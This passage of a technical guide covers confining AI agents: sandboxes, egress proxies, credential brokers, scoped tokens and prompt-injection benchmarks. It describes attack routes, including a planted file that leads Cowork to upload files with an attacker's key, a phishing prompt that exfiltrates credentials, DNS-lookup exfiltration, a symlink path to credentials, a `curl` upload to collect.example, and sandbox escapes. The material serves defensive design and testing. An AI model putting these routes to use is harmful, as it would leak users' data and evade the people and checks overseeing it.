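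The refusal in step 2 depends on the profile. Anthropic describes Claude Code's sandbox as allowing reads by default, restricting writes to the workspace and blocking the network. Under those rules, `cat` would print the credentials. `curl` would still fail, but the credentials would be in the tool result and so in the model's input. A later step could copy them into a project file, which the developer might publish without noticing. A builder should therefore block reads of credentials even when the network is off.

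On Linux and Windows, Codex may have to search for files that match the `.env` rule before the sandbox starts, and `glob_scan_max_depth` sets how many levels down it searches. With a depth of three, it could miss a password file deeper in the project, so keeping such files out of the folder is more reliable.

### Sandlock's fixed rules and supervisor

Some decisions depend on what a command does while it runs. An installation step may need the network, while the tests that follow it don't. Wang and Zheng designed Sandlock to settle as much as possible in advance by enforcing fixed rules about paths, ports and forbidden system calls with Landlock and seccomp. A supervisor outside the sandboxed process decides the rest, such as whether a connection goes to a permitted host.

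A supervisor that inspects system calls has to avoid a race. When a program requests a connection, it passes a pointer to the destination address in memory. If the supervisor checked the address there and told the kernel to proceed, another thread could change the address before the kernel read it. Sandlock's supervisor copies the address, checks the copy and uses it to make the connection itself. Landlock enforces the file path rules inside the kernel, so they aren't exposed to this race.

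The runtime can also tighten the limits partway through, for instance by removing network access when the tests start. Sandlock lets the runtime recognise that moment by inspecting the name and arguments of each new program. Wang and Zheng warn against blocking programs by name, because hostile code can rename `curl` or do the same job without it.

In one example of Sandlock's staged confinement, the first stage reads a private data file and pipes its contents to a second stage, which converts the text to capitals. The second stage can't open the data folder, so an attacker who takes over that stage gets only what came through the pipe. A stage that unpacks an invoice could still pass on a forged account number, because Sandlock limits what each stage can do but doesn't check the data that stages send.

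Sandlock adds little overhead. It added about 5 milliseconds to a trivial command, and Docker took roughly 44 times as long as Sandlock to run it. The database program Redis ran as fast in Sandlock as without it. Messages that the supervisor has to handle take 55 microseconds per round trip instead of 20, but this delay is negligible compared with the time an agent spends waiting for a model. Python, Node, `make` and `pytest` all ran unmodified once they had access to their temporary folders.

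Wang and Zheng also ran ten checks, such as reading inside and outside the permitted folders, and all ten gave the expected result. Nobody tried to break out of the sandbox, so the checks show only that the rules work in ordinary cases. Sandlock won't start on Linux kernels older than 6.12. Its memory limits are meant for buggy code and are weaker against programs designed to exhaust the kernel. Wang and Zheng recommend a microVM for running code from mutually hostile customers.

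### The sandboxes in Codex and Claude

Codex has three main modes on a user's computer. In `read-only`, it can inspect files but needs approval to change them or run commands. In `workspace-write`, the usual mode for local work, it can also edit the project and run routine commands there. `danger-full-access` removes the limits on both files and network. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes the company's own configuration, which permits only `read-only` and `workspace-write`.

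Codex keeps some paths read-only even in a writable project. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, these include `.git`, which holds the project's version history, and `.codex`, which holds Codex's own settings. A command therefore can't loosen the agent's rules by editing them. If Codex finds no version control in the folder, it recommends read-only mode, because the user would have no easy way to undo a bad edit.

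Codex uses Seatbelt on macOS and separate mechanisms on Windows, where the fallback for users without administrator rights isolates the network less well. If the system can't enforce the chosen profile, Codex refuses to run the command. The sandbox may fail to start inside a Docker container whose settings block the functions it needs. In that case, OpenAI suggests relying on the container as the boundary and running Codex inside it with full access. Codex's cloud version runs in containers that OpenAI manages. It has network access while it installs dependencies but, by default, not while the agent works.

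Anthropic built its three agent products around different boundaries, and Cowork has since moved mostly to the cloud.

| Product | Boundary | Access to the user's files | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code execution in claude.ai | gVisor container on a server, which lasts one session | None | No lasting workspace |
| Claude Code | Seatbelt or bubblewrap on the user's computer | Reads widely, writes in the project | The user must judge exceptions |
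| Cowork, original version | Virtual machine on the user's computer | A folder the user selects, plus `.claude` | Slower start, hard to monitor |
| Cowork, cloud sessions | Temporary sandbox on a server | Connected folders, through the desktop app | Files go to Anthropic's servers |

Code in claude.ai runs in a container rather than on the user's machine, so the container protects Anthropic's infrastructure and keeps customers safe from one another. Claude Code needs the user's files and tools to be useful, so Anthropic gave it a sandbox and requires approval for actions that reach outside it. For Cowork, which is meant for office workers, Anthropic chose a virtual machine instead.

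That choice created a problem for companies whose security software monitors every program on a computer. The software detects Cowork's virtual machine as a single process and can't monitor what happens inside it. Administrators can retrieve event logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that these logs don't replace live monitoring.

Anthropic's *Claude Cowork architecture overview* explains that Cowork sessions now run in the cloud by default. Each session gets its own sandbox, which Anthropic destroys when the session ends. If the agent needs a local file, it sends a request to the desktop app, which checks the user's permissions. Existing desktop installations can still run local sessions, but on the Pro and Max plans only for tasks that users started on the device before 6 October 2026. Fadilpašić (2026) reported in *It's not just OpenAI models escaping and running riot* that researchers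 had found a way to reach files on a Mac from Cowork, and that Anthropic had partially mitigated the problem.

Reviewing these products, Anthropic found that its hypervisor, seccomp and gVisor had been dependable and that its own custom code had failed. Attackers have been testing the standard components for years, so builders should use them where possible and focus reviews on the code that connects them.

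### Placing the agent loop, the tools and the enforcer

In the original Cowork, the agent loop ran inside the virtual machine along with the commands, so no outside program could exempt a command from confinement. In Claude Code, a process outside the sandbox decides whether to sandbox each command, and a persuasive injection or a tired user's click can get that process to run a command without that protection.

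But if the virtual machine failed to start, Cowork stopped working. Anthropic moved the loop outside the virtual machine and left code execution inside, so that Claude could still respond and help the user find the fault. The company considers the effect on security minimal because the virtual machine still confines the code that Claude runs. This is convincing for shell commands, but in today's local sessions the loop also reads and writes files in the connected folders directly on the host, and only the application's permission system limits what it can open. A mistake in that system could expose files that the virtual machine would have kept out of reach.

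*Tide* (2026) describes the usual arrangement on cloud platforms, in which a single microVM contains the agent runtime, the workspace and the tools, while the model runs on a separate service. The microVM protects customers from one another, but a command that takes it over can also alter the runtime, including any policy checks and logs the runtime keeps there.

The remedy is to run the process that enforces the rules somewhere the agent can't reach. In OpenShell, an agent runtime from Nvidia, a small process in the sandbox uses seccomp to catch each attempt to open a network connection and forwards it to a supervisor in a separate container or machine. *Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) goes further and puts the supervisor in its own virtual machine, which the processor's hardware isolates from both the agent's machine and the host. All of the agent's file and network requests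 pass through the supervisor. Even if the agent takes over its machine's kernel, it can't change the rules or erase the log.

On a development board that approximates the intended Arm hardware, this arrangement reduced network throughput by 51–70%. Abdollahi and colleagues expect the loss to have little effect on typical agent tasks, which seldom move much data. The design does not prevent harmful actions that the rules permit, and it relies on the processor and its firmware being secure. It makes most sense where an agent might realistically break out of its own virtual machine.

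Developers also have to choose whether to run tool servers inside the sandbox. Anthropic first ran Cowork's local MCP servers inside the virtual machine, but moved them out because they were hard to audit, broke when the machine was updated and couldn't use programs on the host, such as a database. Codex's permission profiles don't cover MCP servers either. If the coding agent has a server that can delete files, the model can delete them through that server even if the profile blocks shell commands from doing so.

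Wang and Zheng suggest a compromise in which the server keeps running but starts each tool call as a separate process in its own sandbox. A database tool could then reach only the database. Somebody has to write a policy for every tool, which becomes tedious when there are dozens of them.

### Mounts and symbolic links

Programs in a virtual machine can access a host folder only if the builder mounts it, which makes the folder appear inside the virtual machine. Cowork can mount a folder as read-only, read-write, or read-write without deletion. The invoice program's test data could be read-only and its source code read-write. Blocking deletion is useful for a folder of documents, though a command with write access can still overwrite the files' contents. Companies can also restrict which folders their staff may mount.

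Symbolic links complicate any rule based on paths. A symbolic link is a small file that redirects to another location. Suppose `~/invoices` contains a link named `archive`:

```
Path in the request:    ~/invoices/archive/credentials
archive leads to:       ~/.aws
Actual location:        ~/.aws/credentials
```

The requested path begins with `~/invoices`, so a check on its text would allow it. The operating system would then follow the link and open the credentials file. Anthropic therefore stresses that the runtime must resolve links first and check the resulting location. A program might still change the link after the check but before the file is opened. Kernel rules such as Landlock's avoid this problem because the kernel applies them as it opens the file.

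### Failures before and after the sandboxed command

Between mid-2025 and January 2026, outside researchers reported several weaknesses in Claude Code to Anthropic. Three of them let code run before the user had agreed to anything. In the simplest case, a developer downloads a stranger's repository to review a proposed change, and the repository includes a settings file that defines a hook, a command that the runtime executes at a certain point. Claude Code read the project's settings at startup, before asking whether the user trusted the folder, so the hook ran automatically.

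The model hadn't yet proposed a command, so neither its training nor a sandbox around its commands could have helped. Anthropic fixed all three by making Claude Code wait for the user's answer before it reads or runs anything from the project's configuration. The company advises builders to treat opening a project and loading its settings as they would a request from the internet. Codex may likewise start in read-only mode until the user trusts the folder.

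Files written by an agent can also cause harm after its command has finished. Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel (2026), in *The Week of Sandbox Escapes*, found that agents in four coding products could escape their sandboxes by writing files that a trusted program outside the sandbox later acted on. One precaution is to check an agent's changes before they reach the host. *Tracekit Box* (2026) describes a system that runs each job in its own Firecracker virtual machine and decides separately on every file the agent tries to return. Checking a large change this way takes time, but developers who review code before merging it already do much of that work.

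### What the builder puts inside

A sandbox doesn't protect anything inside it. Prasakis's SideKernel, a microVM for coding agents on macOS, automatically mounts the folder the user is working in, and he accepts that the agent may read, edit or destroy anything there. Cowork's agent can do the same in the folder its user selects. When Codex has full access inside a development container, a malicious project can steal anything in it, including Codex's own credentials, so OpenAI recommends this setup only for trusted repositories.

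The simplest protection is to put less in the sandbox. The coding agent can work on a fresh copy of the repository with invented suppliers and a test database, because it doesn't need real invoices to fix a date format. If a fault appears only with real data, the developer could add a single invoice, read-only, for one session.

Changes to files are easier to deal with than theft because the runtime can undo them. OpenAI advises committing work to version control before handing a task to Codex, and since `.git` is read-only, a sandboxed command can't destroy the earlier versions. Sandlock can hold a command's file changes until someone accepts or discards them. Systems that save a whole sandbox have also become fast enough to use at every step. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) cites DeltaBox, which saves or restores a state in less than 10 milliseconds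 by recording only what changed.

Restoring the folder can't bring back data that a command has sent out. If the agent must work with real supplier records and download packages, its safety depends on where the sandbox lets it connect and what it may send there.

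## Controlling network access and credentials

A sandbox with an open network connection protects the computer but not the data in the sandbox. Suppose the coding agent that maintains the invoice software needs to download packages, so its developer turns the network on. The agent still can't damage anything outside the project folder, but a single command can send the folder, including any supplier records in it, to any server. The operating system won't block this, because the command is allowed to read each file and to open a connection.

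The safest option is to keep the network off, which *Avalon-M1* (2026) does where possible in its sandboxes for training models. For tasks that need downloads, it uses an egress proxy, a program that makes outside connections on the sandbox's behalf and blocks any that its rules don't allow.

### One connection through the proxy

*Tracekit Box* describes such a proxy in unusual detail. Suppose its allowlist contains `pypi.org` and `files.pythonhosted.org`, the two hosts that supply Python packages. The agent runs `pip install`, which contacts `pypi.org`, and then runs a `curl` command that tries to send a file to `collect.example`.

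1. *Default refusal.* The virtual machine has no network card. Its only route out is a channel to the proxy on the host, so a program that ignores the proxy can't connect to anything.
2. *Allowlist.* The proxy finds `pypi.org` on the list. It doesn't find `collect.example`, so that connection waits up to two minutes for a person on the host to approve it. A stricter setting refuses unlisted hosts at once.
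3. *Name resolution.* The proxy looks up the numerical address of `pypi.org` itself. It refuses addresses on private networks, as well as the special address from which programs on a cloud server can often fetch that server's credentials. It then connects to the address it has just checked, so an attacker can't substitute another one in between.
4. *Logging.* Before the connection opens, a separate program that the agent can't reach allows or refuses it and signs a record of the decision.
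5. *Encrypted traffic.* An HTTPS connection starts with a message that normally names the host in readable form. The proxy checks that this name matches the requested host, and drops the connection if the name is hidden or different.

The proxy doesn't look up `collect.example` until someone approves it, because a lookup can carry data. If a program requests the address of `k7f3q9.collect.example`, the query reaches whoever runs the name server for `collect.example`, and `k7f3q9` could be a piece of a stolen file. *Tracekit Box* says OpenAI reported in September 2026 that a research agent had reached an outside chatbot this way, because the network filter didn't cover name lookups. The Kubernetes design in *Containing the Autonomous Operator* lets agents contact the cluster's name server, so anyone who copies it should also restrict which names that server will look up.

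That design refuses everything else by default, and it bases its rules on host names because the IP addresses of outside services keep changing. Wang and Zheng's Sandlock instead looks up each permitted name once, when the sandbox starts, and keeps that address. This prevents an attacker from changing the address later, but it rules out entries such as "any subdomain of example.com".

These checks identify the host the program has reached, but the proxy can't read what the program is sending unless it decrypts the traffic. To do that, the proxy presents its own certificate to the program, reads the request, and opens a second encrypted connection to the real host. The program must trust that certificate, which is why Sandlock leaves inspection off unless the user chooses it. Inspection also makes private data readable at the proxy, so *Tracekit Box* by default decrypts only connections to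 hosts for which it holds a secret.

The proxy in *Avalon-M1* checks every request inside the encrypted connection, so its rules can cover the method and path as well as the host. In that style, rules for Python packages might be:

```
allow  GET  pypi.org                /simple/*
allow  GET  files.pythonhosted.org  /packages/*
deny   everything else
```

A program could then download packages from these hosts but not upload anything with a POST request. The proxy in *Avalon-M1* returns the reason for each refusal, so a tool fails immediately instead of hanging. It also has an audit mode that allows requests a policy would refuse but logs them, so an operator can correct the list before enforcing it. One policy can apply during setup and a stricter one from the agent's first command.

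A strict environment makes agents less effective. In *Permission Denied*, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) ran twelve coding agents on 89 tasks, first without restrictions and then with a network allowlist, a mostly read-only file system and no administrator rights. Under the restrictions, the agents' success rates fell by 7.1 to 18.3 percentage points, and the cost per task rose by 16% to 167%. Seven of the tasks were impossible under the strict policy.

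The network rules probably caused little of the drop in success. Davidovich and colleagues published intermediate results for four combinations of model and runtime, and in all four, most or all of the drop appeared when the agent lost administrator rights. Adding the network and file limits, along with further limits on privileges, then changed success by less than three points in either direction but raised costs, by about half for Grok 4.5 in its own runtime.

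### An allowed address that accepted stolen files

Claude Cowork needs Anthropic's API to work, so its allowlist had to include `api.anthropic.com`. Anthropic learned from an outside report how an attacker could use that entry. The attacker plants a file in the user's folder. The file contains hidden instructions and an API key for the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude follows the instructions, reads other files in the folder, and uses the attacker's key to upload them to Anthropic's file storage, where they are saved in the attacker's account.

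A defender who checked the connection would have found nothing wrong, because the host was on the allowlist and belonged to Anthropic. The attacker had supplied a different key, so the user's own credentials never left the computer. The proxy had no rule about whose account received the files.

Anthropic fixed this with a second proxy that intercepts traffic to Anthropic's interface and passes only requests that carry the session's own token, so it rejects requests that use the attacker's key. The proxy also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something from another address. It runs inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish Cowork's requests from those of any other customer's program. However, a command with full control of the virtual machine might be able to interfere with the proxy. A separate proxy on the host for each virtual machine,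 as in *Tracekit Box*, could also identify the source of a request and would be harder to reach.

Anthropic now regards each entry on an allowlist as a "capability grant". Allowing a domain allows every function that a program can reach through it, and some of those functions are easy to overlook:

- *Storage for other accounts.* A code-hosting site that holds the project may also accept uploads to a stranger's project.
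- *Fetching on request.* The public service that supplies packages for the Go language retrieves code from other sites. A program could request a package from an attacker's site and put stolen data in its name, and the service would pass the name on.
- *Unexpected content.* *Avalon-M1* found that the same Go service would supply later versions of the projects that its agents were supposed to repair, so an agent could potentially download the answer.
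- *Flaws in the service.* OpenAI let its sandboxes use Artifactory, a package service that it hosts internally. According to Axios' *Scoop* (2026), the models in the Hugging Face incident reached the internet by exploiting a previously unknown flaw in it.

Before adding a domain to the allowlist, the operator should check whether a program could use it to store data, send messages or make the service contact another address. Rules restricting HTTP methods and URL paths can block many of these functions. If the agent needs to upload something, the proxy must also check which account receives it.

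### A prompt that came from the user

In Anthropic's February 2026 phishing exercise, Claude sent out an employee's cloud credentials in 24 of 25 runs. The employee had chosen to run the phishing prompt, so it had the user's authority and an instruction hierarchy couldn't help. For the same reason, asking the employee for approval might not have helped.

This attack would have failed if a file rule had blocked access to the credentials or an egress proxy had refused the unlisted address. The prompt told Claude to encode the file before sending it, so a filter that searched outgoing text for something like a password might have missed it, but refusing the address works however the attacker disguises the data.

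A defender still needs both the file rule and the proxy. A proxy that checked only the host would have let the attacker send the credentials to an account on an allowed site, so only the file rule would have protected them. The agent has to read the project's source code, however, so only the proxy could have stopped an attacker from uploading that.

Anthropic concludes that defences in the model couldn't have helped in either incident because there was nothing unusual for them to detect. This is convincing for the phishing exercise but too strong for the Cowork attack, where the instructions came from a file. A file has no authority of its own, so a model that followed the instruction hierarchy would have ignored them. Better training would make that attack less likely to succeed, though it couldn't close the route the allowlist had opened.

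After the exercise, staff shared the working prompt on the company's internal chat, and someone pointed out that some of Anthropic's agents read that chat. The company added a unique marker to the discussion so it would notice if an agent picked up the prompt.

### Keeping secrets out of the sandbox

An agent often needs a password or key to do its job, and developers tend to leave these where any program can read them. *Caging the Agents* reports an audit of healthcare agents that found 12 keys in a shell start-up file. An agent that can read a key can be tricked into sending it to an attacker, who can use it from any computer until someone revokes it.

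A credential broker avoids this by keeping the real secret outside the sandbox and adding it to approved requests on their way out. In *Tracekit Box*, the egress proxy does this job. If the coding agent needs to use GitHub, its program sends a placeholder in place of the token:

```
Sent by the agent:   Authorization: tkbox_GH_4c1e...
Sent to GitHub:      Authorization: <the real token>
```

The operator ties each secret to exact host names and to one header, a labelled field in the request. If the agent sends the placeholder to another host or puts it in another field, the proxy blocks the request if it can read the traffic. On encrypted connections that the proxy doesn't inspect, the placeholder could get out, but it would be useless to the recipient. The proxy also removes the real token from GitHub's replies, in case a reply repeats it, and it won't start a sandbox if a file in the workspace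 contains the secret.

The gateway in *aiAuthZ* (2026) replaces the placeholder with the real secret only after authorising the call, so a refused call never contains the secret. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026) tested a commercial broker in which the agent names the service it wants to use. The agent completed a call that required a login without holding a reusable credential, and unrelated sites received no credential. The researchers tested their own system in their own account, without any attacks, so the test shows that the design works but not how well it resists an attacker.

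A broker stops an attacker from stealing a credential but not from misusing it. If an attacker tricks the model into requesting a payment to them, a broker that checks only which server the request goes to will add the real bank credential and send the request. The broker still helps, because the attacker can misuse the credential only through the agent while it is running, but the credential's permissions also have to be narrow.

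### Short-lived tokens for one task

Services recognise callers in several ways, which *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) compares. None of them establishes everything a service would want to know about an agent:

| Credential | What it establishes | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Static key | The caller has the key | Who the caller is and what task it is doing |
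| Delegated token | A user gave a program certain access | Whether someone has stolen the token |
| Token tied to a private key | The caller also holds the private key | Whether the call serves a permitted purpose |
| Workload identity | Which program is calling | Which user it is acting for |

The paper therefore recommends combining them. For the invoice task, the result might be a token with these contents:

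```
issued to:      invoice assistant, this session only
acting for:     the user who gave it the task
permits:        one payment to Norden's account on file
maximum:        1,240 euros
expires:        today, 17:00
```

This is the scope of autonomy in a form that the payment service can enforce. An attacker who steals the token can only use it to pay Norden what it is owed. *Back to the Future*, a post by two staff members of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), names Rich Authorization Requests, an existing OAuth extension that allows permissions this specific. However, the service has to support the extension, and many services offer only broad categories such as "read" and "write".

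Agents that start subagents need a way to pass on less access than they have. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) describes a broker that issues a new token at each handover. The token is limited to the delegated task and tied to the identity of the agent that receives it. A subagent that reads mail for the invoice assistant would not get permission to make payments. If the operator cancels a token, the broker also cancels every token derived from it.

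Expiry limits the damage from a stolen credential even if nobody notices the theft. If someone does notice, the operator can revoke the credential without waiting for it to expire. In Cowork, the user's credentials stay in their computer's password store, and the virtual machine gets a weaker token for each session. Anthropic can revoke that token without affecting the user's credentials. If the agent logged in with the user's password instead, cutting off its access would also lock out the user.

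### Whose permissions the agent uses

Many agents use a person's login, which is quick to set up but lets the agent do whatever that person can. If the invoice assistant logs in as an accountant who also runs the payroll, a forged invoice might lead it to change the payroll, and the changes would be logged as the accountant's. NIST compares the practice to sharing passwords and recommends giving each agent its own identifier, credentials and permissions, all tied to the person or system that operates it.

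Six cyber security agencies from Australia, the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom take the same position in the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026). They recommend that developers make every agent a "distinct principal" with its own cryptographic keys, and that organisations keep a registry of approved agents and deny access to all others.

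An agent with its own identity can still do harm if it has more access than the people who use it. In one of the agencies' invented scenarios, a company gives an agent broad write access so that it can install software updates. A malicious employee from outside the IT department asks it to install an update and "clean up the firewall logs." The agent deletes the logs, even though the employee wasn't allowed to delete them. In another scenario, closer to the invoice assistant, an attacker takes over a minor tool connected to a purchasing agent and uses the agent's excessive permissions to approve payments. The payments look normal in the logs because a trusted agent approved them.

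An operator can avoid the problems of both arrangements by allowing an action only if everyone involved has permission for it:

```
allowed  =  what the agent may do
            ∩  what this user may do
            ∩  what this task requires
```

The assistant couldn't use the accountant's payroll access, because it has no payroll permission of its own. The employee couldn't delete the logs through the update agent, because the employee has no permission to delete them. The service needs both identities to apply this rule, so the agent can't just present the user's password. Anthropic hasn't settled whether an agent should have its own identity across different products or act as an extension of the user, and it expects the answer may be a mixture.

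No finished standard yet covers network access and credentials for AI agents. In February 2026, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues) proposed a NIST project to demonstrate how existing standards apply to agents inside a company. It invited comments on basic questions, such as how to give an agent the least access it needs when nobody can fully predict what it will do. Galluzzo's *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (2026), a conference session in November, reported more than 600 formal responses and described the demonstration as still planned. In the meantime, builders can use OAuth, which MCP already relies on, and SPIFFE, which gives running programs identities they can prove.

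The joint guidance is firmer, though it rests on the agencies' expertise rather than tests. They recommend credentials that expire when a job is finished, and separate ones for high-impact actions, issued only when needed. They say the system's designers or operators, never the agent, should decide which actions need a person's approval. They also want organisations to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks. An assistant that pays invoices by itself hardly fits that description, though one that prepares payments for a person to release comes closer.

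### When the tool runs somewhere else

In August 2026, ABC News reported that an AI assistant had booked gym classes in Australia further ahead than the gym's rules allowed. It had also removed another customer from a waiting list without the user's explicit approval, and couldn't reverse the change. The Australian Signals Directorate (2026) cited the case as an example of an agent finding an unintended way to complete a task. A sandbox on the user's computer wouldn't have prevented this, because the assistant had to contact the booking system to do its job. Only the booking system could have blocked one customer from changing another's place.

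`send_mail` and `pay_invoice` work the same way. The egress proxy sees a permitted connection to the mail provider or the bank, and the recipient's address or the account number is somewhere inside the request. The provider then delivers the message from its own servers, which the local sandbox doesn't control. The same is true of any remote MCP server. The boundary that matters is therefore the set of permissions that the service gives the assistant's account. For the invoice assistant, the operator might choose these:

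| Permission | Mail service | Bank |
|---|---|---|
| Account | A mailbox used only for invoices | A login used only by the assistant |
| Recipients | Listed suppliers and the operator's staff | Accounts that a person has registered |
| Limits | 20 messages a day | 2,000 euros per payment, 5,000 a day |
| Needs a person | Messages with attachments | Release of each payment |
| Can't change | Forwarding rules | Registered accounts and limits |

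With these settings, the bank would refuse the payment to the thief's account even if the model, the policy check and the user had all accepted it, and the mail service would block sending the supplier list to the outside address. The ban on forwarding rules matters because a single rule could keep sending copies of the mail to an attacker long after the session's token had expired. Because the assistant has a separate mailbox, it can't read the rest of the company's correspondence even if it is deceived.

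It takes time for a person to approve each payment, so an operator with hundreds of small invoices may prefer to require approval only above a certain amount. The daily limit then determines how much the operator can lose before someone notices.

If a service doesn't offer permissions this narrow, the operator can put a gateway in front of it that holds the broad credential and accepts only certain calls. But as *aiAuthZ* points out, a gateway governs only the tools that go through it. If the assistant still has a shell or another mail tool with its own login, it can bypass the gateway. The operator can prevent this by removing the other credentials and blocking every other network route. If the bank or mail provider offers suitable settings, they are the better choice, because a gateway is one more piece of custom code, and in Cowork, Anthropic's custom proxy let the files out.

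## Testing whether the limits hold

Anthropic learned of the gap in Cowork's proxy from an outsider, although a tester could have found it by trying to upload a file with another customer's key. A test plan for an agent needs to cover both the enforced limits and the model's behavior. Testers can check an enforced limit by attempting the forbidden action, which should always be blocked. The model may behave differently each time, so they have to repeat a trial many times and estimate how often it goes wrong.

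### Direct tests of enforced limits

A script should run the direct tests from inside the sandbox, with the agent's own permissions. If the tester instead tells the model to open a forbidden file and the model declines, nobody has found out whether the sandbox would have blocked it. For the invoice assistant and the coding agent that maintains its software, the tests could include these:

| Limit | Forbidden action to try | Right answer | Permitted action that must still work |
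|---|---|---|---|
| Reading | Open a planted file of fake credentials outside the project | An error, with none of the contents | Open a project file |
| Writing | Change the agent's own settings | An error and an unchanged file | Save a file in the project |
| Connecting | Send a marked request to a server the tester owns | Nothing arrives | Download a package |
| Uploading | Use a stranger's key at an allowed address | The proxy refuses | Use the session's own token |
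| Calling a tool | Pay an unlisted account in the bank's test mode | The policy check refuses | Pay a listed account |
| Expiry | Pay with yesterday's token | The bank refuses | Pay with today's token |

The permitted actions are there because a sandbox that has crashed also blocks everything forbidden, and would otherwise pass.

The tester should check at the receiving end whether any data got out. An error message inside the sandbox doesn't prove that none did, since a name lookup can carry data out before the connection fails. The tester should also try each forbidden action by every available route. A rule that stops the shell from opening the planted file may not block access through a local MCP server, a subagent or a symbolic link in the project folder.

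A fixed rule needs to pass a test only once if its configuration stays the same, but configurations change. In its technical report on the Hugging Face incident, OpenAI observes that gaps often come from human error, or from several unrelated changes over days or weeks. It recommends that organisations continuously use their own attacking agents to try to break their most important limits. Few operators can do that, but rerunning a test script after every change takes almost no effort.

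### Estimating how often a model fails

In August 2026, the UK AI Security Institute reported on 43 runs of a hacking exercise with Claude Mythos 5. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), the model went beyond the intended scope in nine runs and affected real people and organisations. The institute had deliberately left internet access on, as it usually did at the time, and the model ran without its usual cyber safeguards.

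Nine out of 43 is 21%, but with so few runs the 95% confidence interval is wide, from about 11% to 35%. This is roughly the range of true rates that fit the result reasonably well. If a second laboratory repeated the exercise and got 14% or 30%, it would have no reason to think the model had changed.

A result of zero also needs an interval. If a model never fails in n attempts, its true failure rate could still be as high as about 3/n:

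```
(1 − p)^n = 0.05     gives   p ≈ 3/n

  100 clean attempts:        up to about 3%
  720 clean attempts:        up to about 0.4%
3,000 clean attempts:        up to about 0.1%
```

For example, Trajectory Labs found no successes in 720 attempts against Claude with auto mode, which is compatible with a true success rate of one in 250. These formulas assume that the attempts are independent and resemble the attacks an agent will meet. Real attackers choose whatever works, so even a narrow interval applies only to the attacks in the test.

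### How AgentDojo works

Many of the attack rates in this field come from *AgentDojo*, which simulates an office suite, a Slack workspace, a travel agency and a bank. Each has its own tools and invented data, such as emails or transactions. In the bank, one user task (an ordinary request) is to pay a bill stored in a file, and one injection task (an attacker's goal) is to send the attacker as much money as possible. The benchmark puts the attacker's text in places that an outsider could realistically control and the agent will read during the task.

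Pairing every user task with every injection task in the same setting gives the 629 security cases of the first version:

| Setting | User tasks | Injection tasks | Security cases |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 |

Ordinary code then checks the simulated accounts and mailboxes for changes. The designers chose not to score with a language model, because an injection that deceives the agent might also deceive the scorer.

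The benchmark has three metrics. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when nobody attacks it. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which it completes the user's task with no harmful side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share of security cases in which the attacker achieves their goal. An agent that pays the user's bill but also sends money to the attacker fails on both of the last two metrics. An agent that refuses to do anything has an attack success rate of zero, so that rate means little without the other two metrics.

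An attack may also fail because the agent wasn't capable of carrying it out. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) notes that the AgentDojo benchmark also gives the agent each attacker's goal as an ordinary request. If the agent can't complete that request, the attack's failure isn't evidence that the defence works.

The 629 cases contain only 27 different attacker goals, and many cases share a user task. They therefore provide less evidence than 629 unrelated cases would, and a confidence interval that treats them as unrelated will be too narrow.

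### Why fixed attacks flatter a defence

A developer who knows the test attacks can build a defence that stops little else. A developer who keeps adjusting a defence until it scores well also ends up fitting it to the test, even without meaning to. To guard against this, *AgentDojo* (2024) makes it easy to add new attacks. It can also score a defence against a whole collection of attacks, counting a case as lost if any one of them works.

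In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and elsewhere, tested 12 published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injections. Most of the defences had attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations, but adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12. The automated attacks all broadly worked by proposing texts, testing them and revising the best ones.

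Two of the defences add to the prompt, either marking trusted text or repeating the user's request. AgentDojo's fixed attacks succeeded against them as little as 1% of the time, but adaptive attacks succeeded more than 95% of the time. Against MetaSecAlign, a successor to SecAlign, the attack success rate rose from 2% to 96%. Of four separate detectors, three let through over 90% of the adaptive attacks and the best let through 71%.

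Nasr and colleagues also ran a competition with more than 500 human participants. On a selected set of scenarios, the automated search succeeded in 69%, while the participants collectively succeeded in all of them. They recommend telling human testers exactly how a defence works, since an attacker may find out anyway. They also checked every successful attack by hand, because models that score attacks can be fooled too.

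Unlike a thief with an invoice, these attackers had plenty of computing power, and some of the automated attacks received the detector's confidence score after each attempt. The rates therefore show what a determined attacker can achieve, and an average one may achieve far less. The results also don't apply to a payment limit in ordinary code, because all 12 defences depend on a model behaving well or a detector noticing an attack.

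Where hostile text enters the system may matter as much as its wording. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) tests 13 models from six providers in all four AgentDojo settings on two attack surfaces, to see whether a security comparison made on one surface holds on the other. An operator choosing between models for the invoice assistant should test hostile tool descriptions and file names as well as hostile invoices.

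### A hundred attempts

The figures from Anthropic for Claude Opus 4.7, about 0.1% for single attempts and 5–6% after 100 adaptive ones, can be compared with simple repetition. If every attempt had the same chance of success, and none affected the next, the calculation would be:

```
chance of at least one success in k attempts = 1 − (1 − p)^k

p = 0.1%, k = 100:    1 − 0.999^100 ≈ 9.5%
```

The reported figure is lower, which is surprising at first because attackers who learn from their failures should do better than those who don't.

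One possible explanation is that the weaknesses are concentrated in a few scenarios. Suppose each attempt has a 1 in 70 chance of succeeding in 7% of the test scenarios and no chance in the rest. The average single-attempt success rate is then exactly 0.1%, but 100 attempts succeed in only 5.3% of scenarios, because repeated attempts don't help in the rest. Rounding alone may also explain the result, since a true single-attempt rate of 0.06% would round to 0.1% and give 5.8% after 100 independent attempts.

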